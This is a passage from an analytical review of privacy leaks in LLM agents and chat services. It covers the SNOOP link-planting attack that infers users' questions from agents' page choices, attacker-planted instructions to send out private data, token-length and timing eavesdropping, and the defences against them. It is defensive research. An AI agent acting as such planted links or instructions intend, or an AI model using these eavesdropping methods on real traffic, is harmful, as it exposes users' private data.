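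Liang and colleagues also planted direct instructions telling the agents to send out private data. These attacks delivered the complete secret in only 0.38% of runs, compared with the 89% that Lan and colleagues achieved against a small model. The instructions came from an older collection, and newer ones might work better. Still, the indirect route worked far better here, which weakens the argument that attackers have no reason to use indirect leaks.

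### Four defences that barely helped

The researchers then repeated the attack with four defences in place:

- Spotlighting marks text from web pages so that the model can recognise it as data.
- Firewalls removes suspected injections from incoming pages and unnecessary details from outgoing requests.
- Task Shield checks whether each tool call contributes to the user's task.
- FIDES checks secrecy and trust labels before each call.

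| Defence | F1, StackExchange | F1, conversations | F1, profiles | Readable paths, StackExchange | Readable paths, conversations |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| None | 0.89 | 0.79 | 0.80 | 94% | 83% |
| Spotlighting | 0.86 | 0.78 | 0.77 | 89% | 83% |
| Firewalls | 0.88 | 0.78 | 0.77 | 87% | 80% |
| Task Shield | 0.88 | 0.76 | 0.77 | 88% | 81% |
| FIDES | 0.87 | 0.77 | 0.77 | 92% | 77% |

None of the defences lowered an F1 score by more than 0.03. Some also prevented a few paths, which the F1 scores don't count. If missing paths are scored as zero, the largest drop in the question scores is about 0.07, so the F1 scores slightly understate the defences' effect.

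Spotlighting, Firewalls and Task Shield fail because the links don't need to contain any instructions to neutralise, the address of the chosen page has no private details to remove, and following a relevant reference is the kind of action that Task Shield approves. Liang and colleagues propose a different kind of defence, Selection-Obfuscated Retrieval, which hides the agent's choice among other downloads.

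### Was FIDES set up as intended?

The result for FIDES is consistent with its stated scope. Costa and colleagues guarantee explicit secrecy, which allows an observer to learn something from the agent's choice of action, and SNOOP relies on that kind of leak.

The test may not have used FIDES as its designers intended. FIDES treats the user's message as public by default, although developers can choose another label. Liang and colleagues labelled the user's question and other private context confidential, which was sensible because FIDES would otherwise have had nothing to protect in the StackExchange test.

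The new label should have made web research almost impossible, because the model's search terms would inherit it and FIDES's secrecy rule would stop the agent from sending them to a public website. Yet 92% of the StackExchange runs still produced a readable path, so the tested version must have allowed most web requests, through either an exception or a narrower rule.

Liang and colleagues describe the labels and the check before each call in their set-up, but not the variables in which FIDES hides untrusted results or the second model that reads them. If the test left these out, the main model could compare the attacker's links directly. In the full design, it would have to open the variable or query the second model about the contents.

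The full design might not have stopped SNOOP either. If the model passed a link's address by variable name, the address would keep the public label of the attacker's page, and FIDES could approve the request even if the model had picked that address based on private data. The test is good evidence that label checks on arguments miss this leak, but its scores apply only to one configuration of FIDES.

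A system that tracks implicit flows could block the request. In LLMbda, for instance, a developer could label the question secret and the website's log public. But the agent then could not use the question to choose web pages, which is most of what a research agent does. Nobody appears to have tested SNOOP against such a system.

### A search that found no indirect leaks

Neither Ogundoyin and Ikram's reconstruction tests nor their behavioural test confirmed an indirect leak. This looks like the opposite result, but the two studies differ in almost every important respect.

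| | SNOOP | Ogundoyin and Ikram |
|---|---|---|
| Attacker | Writes the options and adapts them to earlier choices | Reads messages, logs or files, but changes nothing |
| Secret | The subject of a question, or facts about the user | One private value, such as an account number or a diagnosis |
| Effect of the secret on the task | Determines what the agent looks for | May have no effect on what the agent does next |
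| Successful recovery | Matching concepts or facts, with half credit for near misses | The private value itself, confirmed by hand |
| Models | GPT-5.5, Claude Sonnet 4.6 and Gemini 3.6 Flash | Mainly Qwen3-32B |

How much an agent's choice of pages and tools reveals probably depends most on how the secret affects the task. In one pair of runs, Ogundoyin and Ikram changed a private value from 63000 to 75267. An agent that only has to copy the number into a report has no reason to take different steps for each value. There is then no side channel by Shahriar and colleagues' definition, however good the observer is. By contrast, a diagnosis that determines which clinic to book can change the agent's steps.

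The researchers also used a stricter standard for success than SNOOP did. An automatic judge flagged 550 apparent reconstructions, and the researchers rejected them all on inspection. In 60 of them, one agent had received the value directly, so there was nothing to reconstruct. In two others, the judge had relied on a general similarity of topic, which might have earned some credit under SNOOP's scoring.

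The behavioural test looked for a hidden fingerprint by comparing features such as the number of tool calls. This is a reasonable method, but it could miss which page or tool an agent selects, which is often the most informative part of its behaviour.

Another of their tests fits SNOOP's result fairly well. They compared real pairs of runs, which shared a task and differed only in the private value, with artificial pairs from different scenarios in the same field. A classifier could tell a real pair from an artificial one about 87% of the time after one turn and 71% after twenty, compared with 50% for guessing. So the agents' behaviour depended noticeably on the task, though there was no sign that it depended on the private value.

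In 61% to 63% of the scenarios, the agents in this study also directly disclosed at least one private value to someone without permission to see it. Ogundoyin and Ikram are therefore right to treat direct leaks as the main problem in the systems they tested. Their result doesn't show that an agent's choices are safe when the secret determines the choice, or when an attacker designs the options.

### Shopping on real websites

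An observer may learn something from an agent's choices even without designing the options. Online shops, for example, already offer thousands of products and categories and record what visitors click. Roh, Bagdasarian and colleagues (2026), in *SPILLage*, ran shopping agents on the live Amazon and eBay websites. They used 180 tasks, two agent frameworks and three OpenAI models (GPT-4o, o3 and o4-mini, all now old), for 1,080 runs in total.

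Each prompt mixed facts the agent needed with facts it didn't. In one example, a user with type 2 diabetes wants glucose test strips, and the prompt also reveals that she is divorced. The agent could disclose the divorce by typing it into the search box, but also by clicking on a divorce-party product or scrolling through products for single mothers.

Agents disclosed information through clicks, scrolls and filters about five times as often as through typed text. On Amazon alone, agents using GPT-4o made 1,151 disclosures through actions that referred directly to an irrelevant fact. Removing these facts from the prompts raised task success by up to 17.9%, which suggests that they had been influencing the agents.

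But Amazon couldn't necessarily have inferred all these facts. Roh and colleagues used GPT-4o mini to identify the disclosures, and gave it the user's prompt, a list of the irrelevant facts and the agent's stated next goal. A shop has none of this information. A customer who clicks on a divorce-party product might be buying it for a friend. The study therefore measures how often an agent's actions matched private facts, and it would take a separate test to find out how often an observer could guess them correctly.

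The five-to-one ratio may also depend partly on how people and agents shop. One typed search can lead to many clicks and scrolls, and each gives the agent another chance to disclose something.

### What the attacker must control

SNOOP works only if the agent finds the attacker's link on another page and follows it. In the tests, Liang and colleagues first ran the agents to see which pages they visited early in their research, then put a link on about 2,600 of those pages, about three for each question.

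A real attacker who didn't know the question in advance couldn't choose the pages this way, and would need to control popular pages on many subjects or add links to sites that let anyone post. The 94% success rate in producing a readable path applies only when the attacker already has links in the right places. An attacker interested in one subject, such as a particular disease, would have an easier job.

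The attacker also has to know which visits belong together. SNOOP's reconstruction step starts with paths that are already grouped by question, and a profile requires several questions from the same person. On a busy website, many agents might arrive from the same company's servers at once. The site's operator could connect the steps of one visit by giving each visitor a different set of links, but connecting visits on different days would be harder.

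Users might not notice the attack. In a test with Codex and GPT-5.5, the agent's answers covered 87% of the concepts in the reference answers, down from 93% without the attack, and the median answer was 1.3 times as long. Research also took more time and used more tokens, but a user who hadn't seen a normal run would have little to compare it with.

The agents worked with a saved copy of the web, which made the runs comparable but more orderly than real browsing. On the live web, a search service might supply a stored copy of a page, and the operator would then see no request from the agent. No other research group appears to have repeated the SNOOP tests, and nobody appears to have tried the attack on agents working for real users.

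There is even less evidence about what an agent's choice of tools reveals. A company that provides an agent with several tools can record which one the agent calls, but SNOOP and SPILLage tested only websites, and Ogundoyin and Ikram's behavioural features weren't designed to measure what that choice reveals.

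## What closing the channels costs, and who can do it

Costa and colleagues left the leak through an agent's choices out of FIDES because they thought closing it would stop too much useful work. High overhead could justify leaving out the other channels too, but the overhead varies widely between them. In the example below, hiding the length of each token adds about a tenth to the traffic, while hiding how long the reply took can double the wait.

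### A padding example

Take the assistant that writes 100 tokens if a test result is negative and 140 if it is positive, at 20 ms per token. Suppose each token is sent in its own packet with 102 bytes of overhead, as on DeepSeek's chat website when Zhang and colleagues recorded its traffic for NetEcho. If tokens average 4.5 characters, packets average 106.5 bytes.

The service could pad every token to 16 characters, splitting the occasional longer one, so that every packet is 118 bytes. It could also add dummy packets to the end of each reply, at the same pace as the real ones, so that every reply has 200 packets.

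| Method | Negative result | Positive result | What the eavesdropper learns |
|---|---|---|---|
| No padding | 10,650 bytes in 2.0 s | 14,910 bytes in 2.8 s | The length of every token, and how many there are |
| Every packet padded | 11,800 bytes in 2.0 s | 16,520 bytes in 2.8 s | How many tokens there are |
| Every packet padded, 200 packets per reply | 23,600 bytes in 4.0 s | 23,600 bytes in 4.0 s | Nothing about the result |

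Padding each packet uses 11% more bandwidth and adds no delay, and it would defeat an attack that rebuilds sentences from token lengths. But an eavesdropper can still learn the test result by counting packets. Preventing this takes 58% more bandwidth for a positive result and 122% more for a negative one.

A person reading the reply wouldn't notice the dummy packets, because the text would be complete after 2.0 or 2.8 seconds. An agent would have to wait the full 4 seconds before its next step, because if it sent its next request as soon as the real text ended, the eavesdropper could tell where the dummy packets began.

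Providers have mostly chosen random filler, which is weaker than padding every packet to a fixed length. Adding between 0 and 15 random characters to each packet obscures the length of any one token. Over 100 packets, however, the filler adds up to about 750 bytes, give or take 46, so an eavesdropper can subtract the average to estimate the total length of the text. Random filler also saves only 4 bytes per packet over fixed-length padding, so bandwidth is a poor reason to prefer it.

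### What is left after padding

Zhang and colleagues tested what an eavesdropper could still learn if padding completely hid the token lengths, leaving the classifier with only the number of tokens that arrived together. Random guessing among the ten topics would be right 10% of the time.

| Service | Medical, lengths visible | Medical, lengths hidden | Legal, lengths visible | Legal, lengths hidden |
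|---|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-4o's API | 73.0% | 11.0% | 80.7% | 10.1% |
| Chat website built on GPT | 92.0% | 11.2% | 89.2% | 10.5% |
| DeepSeek's API | 93.7% | 72.6% | 88.7% | 53.8% |
| DeepSeek's chat website | 98.2% | 73.3% | 92.9% | 54.5% |
| Researchers' own server | 91.6% | 77.7% | 89.6% | 64.9% |

Padding would make this attack useless against the GPT services. It would still leave a large leak at DeepSeek, whose model predicts several tokens at a time, and on the researchers' server, which used speculative decoding. With both methods, predictable text arrives in bigger groups. To hide the group sizes, a provider would have to release tokens at a steady pace and give up some of the speed these methods provide.

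This classifier didn't use exact arrival times, so an eavesdropper who used them might do better, even against GPT. McDonald and Bar Or used both sizes and times to test the random filler that Microsoft added to its service. With the filler, their score for recognising money-laundering conversations with GPT-4o mini fell from 97.5% to 92.9%. They think the remaining leak probably comes from timing and total sizes, which is consistent with the arithmetic above.

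That is a small drop, and it's hard to know how much to conclude from it. In the main test, the same type of classifier scored only 91.3% on the same model at Microsoft with no filler. The mix of conversations may have differed between the two tests, which would affect the score.

Microsoft, where McDonald and Bar Or both work, considers what remains "no longer a practical risk". That may well be right for GPT-4o mini on Microsoft's own service, where the model was already a poor target for mass surveillance. The researchers projected that if about one conversation in 10,000 was relevant, and a classifier caught half of the relevant ones in traffic without filler, only 0.4% of the conversations it flagged would be relevant. They didn't publish that projection for traffic with filler, or a score for OpenAI's version of the fix, although GPT-4o mini leaked far more through OpenAI's service.

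### Bigger batches and dummy packets

A service can also send several tokens in each packet. This saves bandwidth because the tokens share one packet's overhead, but it makes the stream jerkier. At 20 ms per token, a batch of five delays the first token by 80 ms, and a batch of 55 delays it by about 1.1 seconds.

McDonald and Bar Or simulated sending tokens in batches of five by merging recorded packets. This removed most of the risk for most of the models they tested, but for GPT-4o mini the attack's score fell only from 98.2% to 94.8%, and they don't know why. Services that already sent tokens in batches were also more vulnerable than expected from the simulation. Gemini 1.5 Flash sent about 55 tokens at a time, and the attack still scored 83.5%.

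Agents could take this much further than chatbots. An agent usually can't run a tool call until the model has finished writing it, so it gains little from streaming. Microsoft suggests that worried users choose models that don't stream, and it seems to me that the calls inside an agent would lose almost nothing by this. The eavesdropper would then see one block of data per call, with a total size and a total time. The builder might still want to stream the final answer to the user.

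Dummy packets scattered through the stream use extra bandwidth but add no delay. McDonald and Bar Or simulated enough of them to double or triple the traffic. The score of an attack using only packet sizes fell from 90.0% to 72.1% for Grok 3 mini and from 98.2% to 93.8% for GPT-4o mini, but did not fall for Gemini 1.5 Flash.

Zhang and colleagues found that adding many dummy packets can work, but adding a few does almost nothing. With one dummy for every five real packets, a classifier could still identify the legal topic 93.9% of the time for DeepSeek and 89.9% for the website built on GPT. With one for every two, accuracy fell to 23.7% for DeepSeek but stayed at 90.1% for the GPT website. With equal numbers of dummy and real packets, accuracy was 12.2% for DeepSeek and 38.6% for the GPT website. Some of their other results are erratic (in one case, accuracy rose from 69% to 94% as dummies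 increased), so the exact thresholds may not be reliable.

### How providers responded to Whisper Leak

McDonald and Bar Or began warning providers in June 2025 and published in November. They write that they notified 28 providers, but the 28 models they tested came from only 11 companies, so they may have counted models instead of providers.

| Provider | Date of the fix | What it changed |
|---|---|---|
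| OpenAI | August 2025 | Added a field called "obfuscation" that holds random text of varying length |
| xAI | August 2025 | Not described |
| Mistral | September 2025 | Added a field called "p" with a similar effect |
| Microsoft | October 2025 | Copied OpenAI's field for models on its Azure service |

Other providers declined, "citing various rationales", and several never answered despite repeated reminders. McDonald and Bar Or don't name either group or say what the rationales were. Google, Anthropic, Amazon, Alibaba and DeepSeek aren't among the four that made changes, but that doesn't show any of them refused. Microsoft's blog post calls the outcome an "industry-wide response", which overstates changes made by four companies. The research paper calls the responses mixed.

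Zhang and colleagues suggest that a provider might hesitate to add a field because most of the industry copies the format of OpenAI's streaming interface, and an extra field can break software that expects the standard format. They consider this compatibility problem harder than writing the code. But OpenAI sets the format, so its decision to add a field should make it easier for other providers to do the same.

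There is little evidence on whether attacks still work after these fixes. All of the Whisper Leak results predate the changes, except the test of Microsoft's filler. The September 2026 benchmark of traffic attacks ran on the researchers' own hardware, so it didn't test the fixes either. NetEcho, which also came out in October 2025, describes OpenAI's API as having no padding, which conflicts with Microsoft's account. The most likely explanation is that Zhang and colleagues recorded their traffic before August.

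They did show that a provider's fix can be undone before the text reaches the user. Many chat websites receive padded or batched text from a provider, unpack it and stream it to their own users one token at a time. The fix then doesn't protect the connection between the website and the user, which is the one an eavesdropper near the user watches. Of the seven kinds of service they examined, only the chatbots that OpenAI, Anthropic and Google run themselves had full protection, with packets of several thousand bytes. Popular toolkits for building chat websites don't support padding, so each developer would have to add it.

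### Separate caches

Giving each customer a separate cache means repeating some work. Suppose 1,000 customers use the same coding agent, and each sends 20 requests while the cache still holds the agent's fixed instructions. The service would process those instructions 1,000 times instead of once with a shared cache, but the other 19,000 requests, 95% of the total, would still reuse the cached work. Only customers who send a single request would get no benefit from caching.

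OpenAI and Anthropic already separate their caches, so they evidently find the cost acceptable. To protect customers who reach a provider through a relay such as OpenRouter, the relay would have to send the provider a marker for each customer, and the provider would have to use it to keep their caches separate.

### Repairs for CaMeL

Tallam and Miller propose changes to the agent itself. They misleadingly write that CaMeL "omits side-channel concerns". According to Narisetty and colleagues, CaMeL's designers demonstrated two working leaks against their own system, one through an indirect dependency and one through an exception that an attacker triggers. The designers also discussed a timing leak that their software mitigates, and concluded that CaMeL is vulnerable to side channels. Tallam and Miller's reference for CaMeL also points to a different paper, on poisoning training data. Their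 proposed changes are still worth considering, but they measured neither the leak that would remain nor the cost.

For a loop whose length depends on a secret, they suggest a cap. If an attacker's loop counts out a PIN but must stop after 15 requests, the server can see at most 16 different counts, or 4 bits, and for almost every PIN it learns only that the number is 15 or more. A cap works badly for ordinary loops, such as one over a patient's diagnoses. If the patient has four, the loop ends before reaching the cap and the count still leaks. If the patient has 20, the answer is incomplete.

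Their other suggestion for loops is to combine repeated calls into one. If every call is the same, as in the PIN example, the agent can fetch the page once and reuse it, which makes fewer requests than the original program. But if each call concerns a different diagnosis, the combined request still contains the whole list, and the website can count the entries. To hide the count, the agent would have to add false diagnoses until every request had the same number.

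Replacing exceptions with structured results slows the system down, because success and failure have to take equally long. If a successful lookup takes 0.2 seconds and a failed one takes 3, every lookup has to take 3 seconds.

Their proposals for fixed schedules and constant running times have the same problem. Suppose the assistant needs 10 seconds for a cardiology record, 15 for psychiatry, 20 for sexual health and 40 for oncology, and that all four are equally likely. The builder can choose when the assistant releases its result.

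| Release time | Average wait | Leak about the clinic |
|---|---|---|
| As soon as it is ready | 21.25 s | 2 bits |
| After 20 s or 40 s | 25 s | 0.81 bits |
| Always after 40 s | 40 s | 0 bits |

Using two release times removes more than half of the leak and adds less than 4 seconds. Removing the rest nearly doubles the average wait. A designer who looks only at the last row might reasonably give up on reducing the timing leak and miss the partial fix in the row above.

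Cryptographic software can run in constant time because its programmers know the longest time an operation can take. A model call has no such limit, because the server's load and the number of tokens both vary. If a run takes 50 seconds, the assistant must either abandon the booking or release it late, which leaks information.

An agent limited to a fixed sequence of tool calls also completes fewer tasks. Costa and colleagues counted far more lost tasks in banking than in office work.

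Zhao and colleagues would move this work out of the agent's program, where a planning model could easily fail to write a careful loop. In AgenticOS, a gateway makes all outside requests on the agent's behalf, so an agent under an attacker's control couldn't skip the padding and pacing. But the gateway can only enforce what the agent declared beforehand. If the declaration lists all four booking pages, the gateway will allow a request to any of them.

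### Downloading the pages the agent doesn't need

Selection-Obfuscated Retrieval (SOR) is Liang and colleagues' defence against their own SNOOP attack. When the agent opens a page, SOR downloads everything the page links to, regardless of what the user asked. The agent then reads the local copies, so the website can't detect which link the agent needed. If the agent needs something that SOR hasn't stored, SOR mixes that request with randomly chosen ones and sends the batch in random order.

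| | StackExchange questions, no defence | StackExchange questions, SOR | User profiles, no defence | User profiles, SOR |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Precision | 0.87 | 0.29 | 0.75 | 0.27 |
| Recall | 0.92 | 0.91 | 0.87 | 0.99 |
| F1 | 0.89 | 0.39 | 0.80 | 0.39 |

F1 falls only because precision falls. The attacker still recovers nearly all of the correct concepts, but they are now mixed with more than twice as many wrong ones. This could be good protection for someone who can plausibly deny an interest in any one topic. It protects less well against an attacker who wants a list of people who might have a particular disease and is willing to check each one. In a slightly different test, random choices brought the attack's F1 down to 0.10, so an F1 of 0.39 probably still reflects a good deal of real information.

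For each StackExchange question, SOR raised the number of downloads from 6.5 to 27.9, model time from 224 to 285 seconds, and tokens from 23,800 to 31,300, an increase of 32%. In the conversations, the agent used 14% more tokens and made 4.5 times as many downloads. Liang and colleagues say that SOR needs no additional model inference, which is true of the downloading step but not of the agent as a whole. They didn't report whether the agents' answers got better or worse.

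They also didn't test an attacker who had adapted to SOR, for example by comparing several visits. Suppose an agent starts with an empty store each day and needs the same page on three different days. Each time, it hides the request among three decoys drawn from 19 other pages. The page it needs appears in all three batches, and the chance that any decoy does the same is less than 8%. Reusing the same decoys would prevent this comparison, but SOR draws them again each time.

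Decoys work for reading because an unnecessary download does little harm. An agent still shouldn't open every link it finds, since some cancel a subscription or confirm an order. The assistant can read the pages of all four clinics, but it can't use decoys when booking, because it would have to make three appointments that the user won't attend.

### Which layer can close which leak

Designers are right to leave some side channels to another layer. A model provider can pad its own packets and separate its customers' caches without knowing anything about the agent or its task, and only the provider can do this for all its customers at once. An agent's builder can sensibly leave these leaks out of a design if the chosen provider has made the changes. Some providers have declined to, so the builder has to check.

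| Leak | Who can close it | What it takes |
|---|---|---|
| Token lengths in the provider's replies | Model provider | Fixed padding, or no streaming |
| Prompts in a cache shared by strangers | Model provider | Separate caches |
| Prompts in a relay's shared account | Relay and provider together | A marker for each customer |
| Token lengths between an app and its user | Whoever runs the app | Padding on that connection too |
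| Number of tool calls, and retries after errors | Agent builder | Fixed counts and uniform handling of errors |
| Which pages the agent reads | Agent builder | Decoy downloads |
| Total time for a task | Provider and agent builder together | A steady token rate and fixed release times |
| Which clinic receives the booking | Neither | A different booking system, or the patient's consent |

The agent builder, not the provider, has to hide how many model calls the assistant makes. If an oncology record leads to two extra calls, an eavesdropper will still count two more replies, even if the provider pads every reply perfectly. To hide the difference, the builder would have to make two dummy calls for each of the other patients and pay for the tokens. If the two calls take 9 seconds and an eighth of patients go to oncology, the dummy calls add almost 8 seconds to the average booking.

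Leaks that take both parties to close are the most likely to stay open, because each party can reasonably say that its own part works. A provider that sends padded text to a chat website has done its part, and the website's developer may believe that the provider has solved the problem. The user can then end up with no protection even though neither party was careless.

No amount of padding or pacing would protect the clinic booking, because neither hides a request from its recipient. The clinics could instead share one page and sort patients after their bookings arrive. This would be cheap, but only the clinics and their hosting company can make the change.
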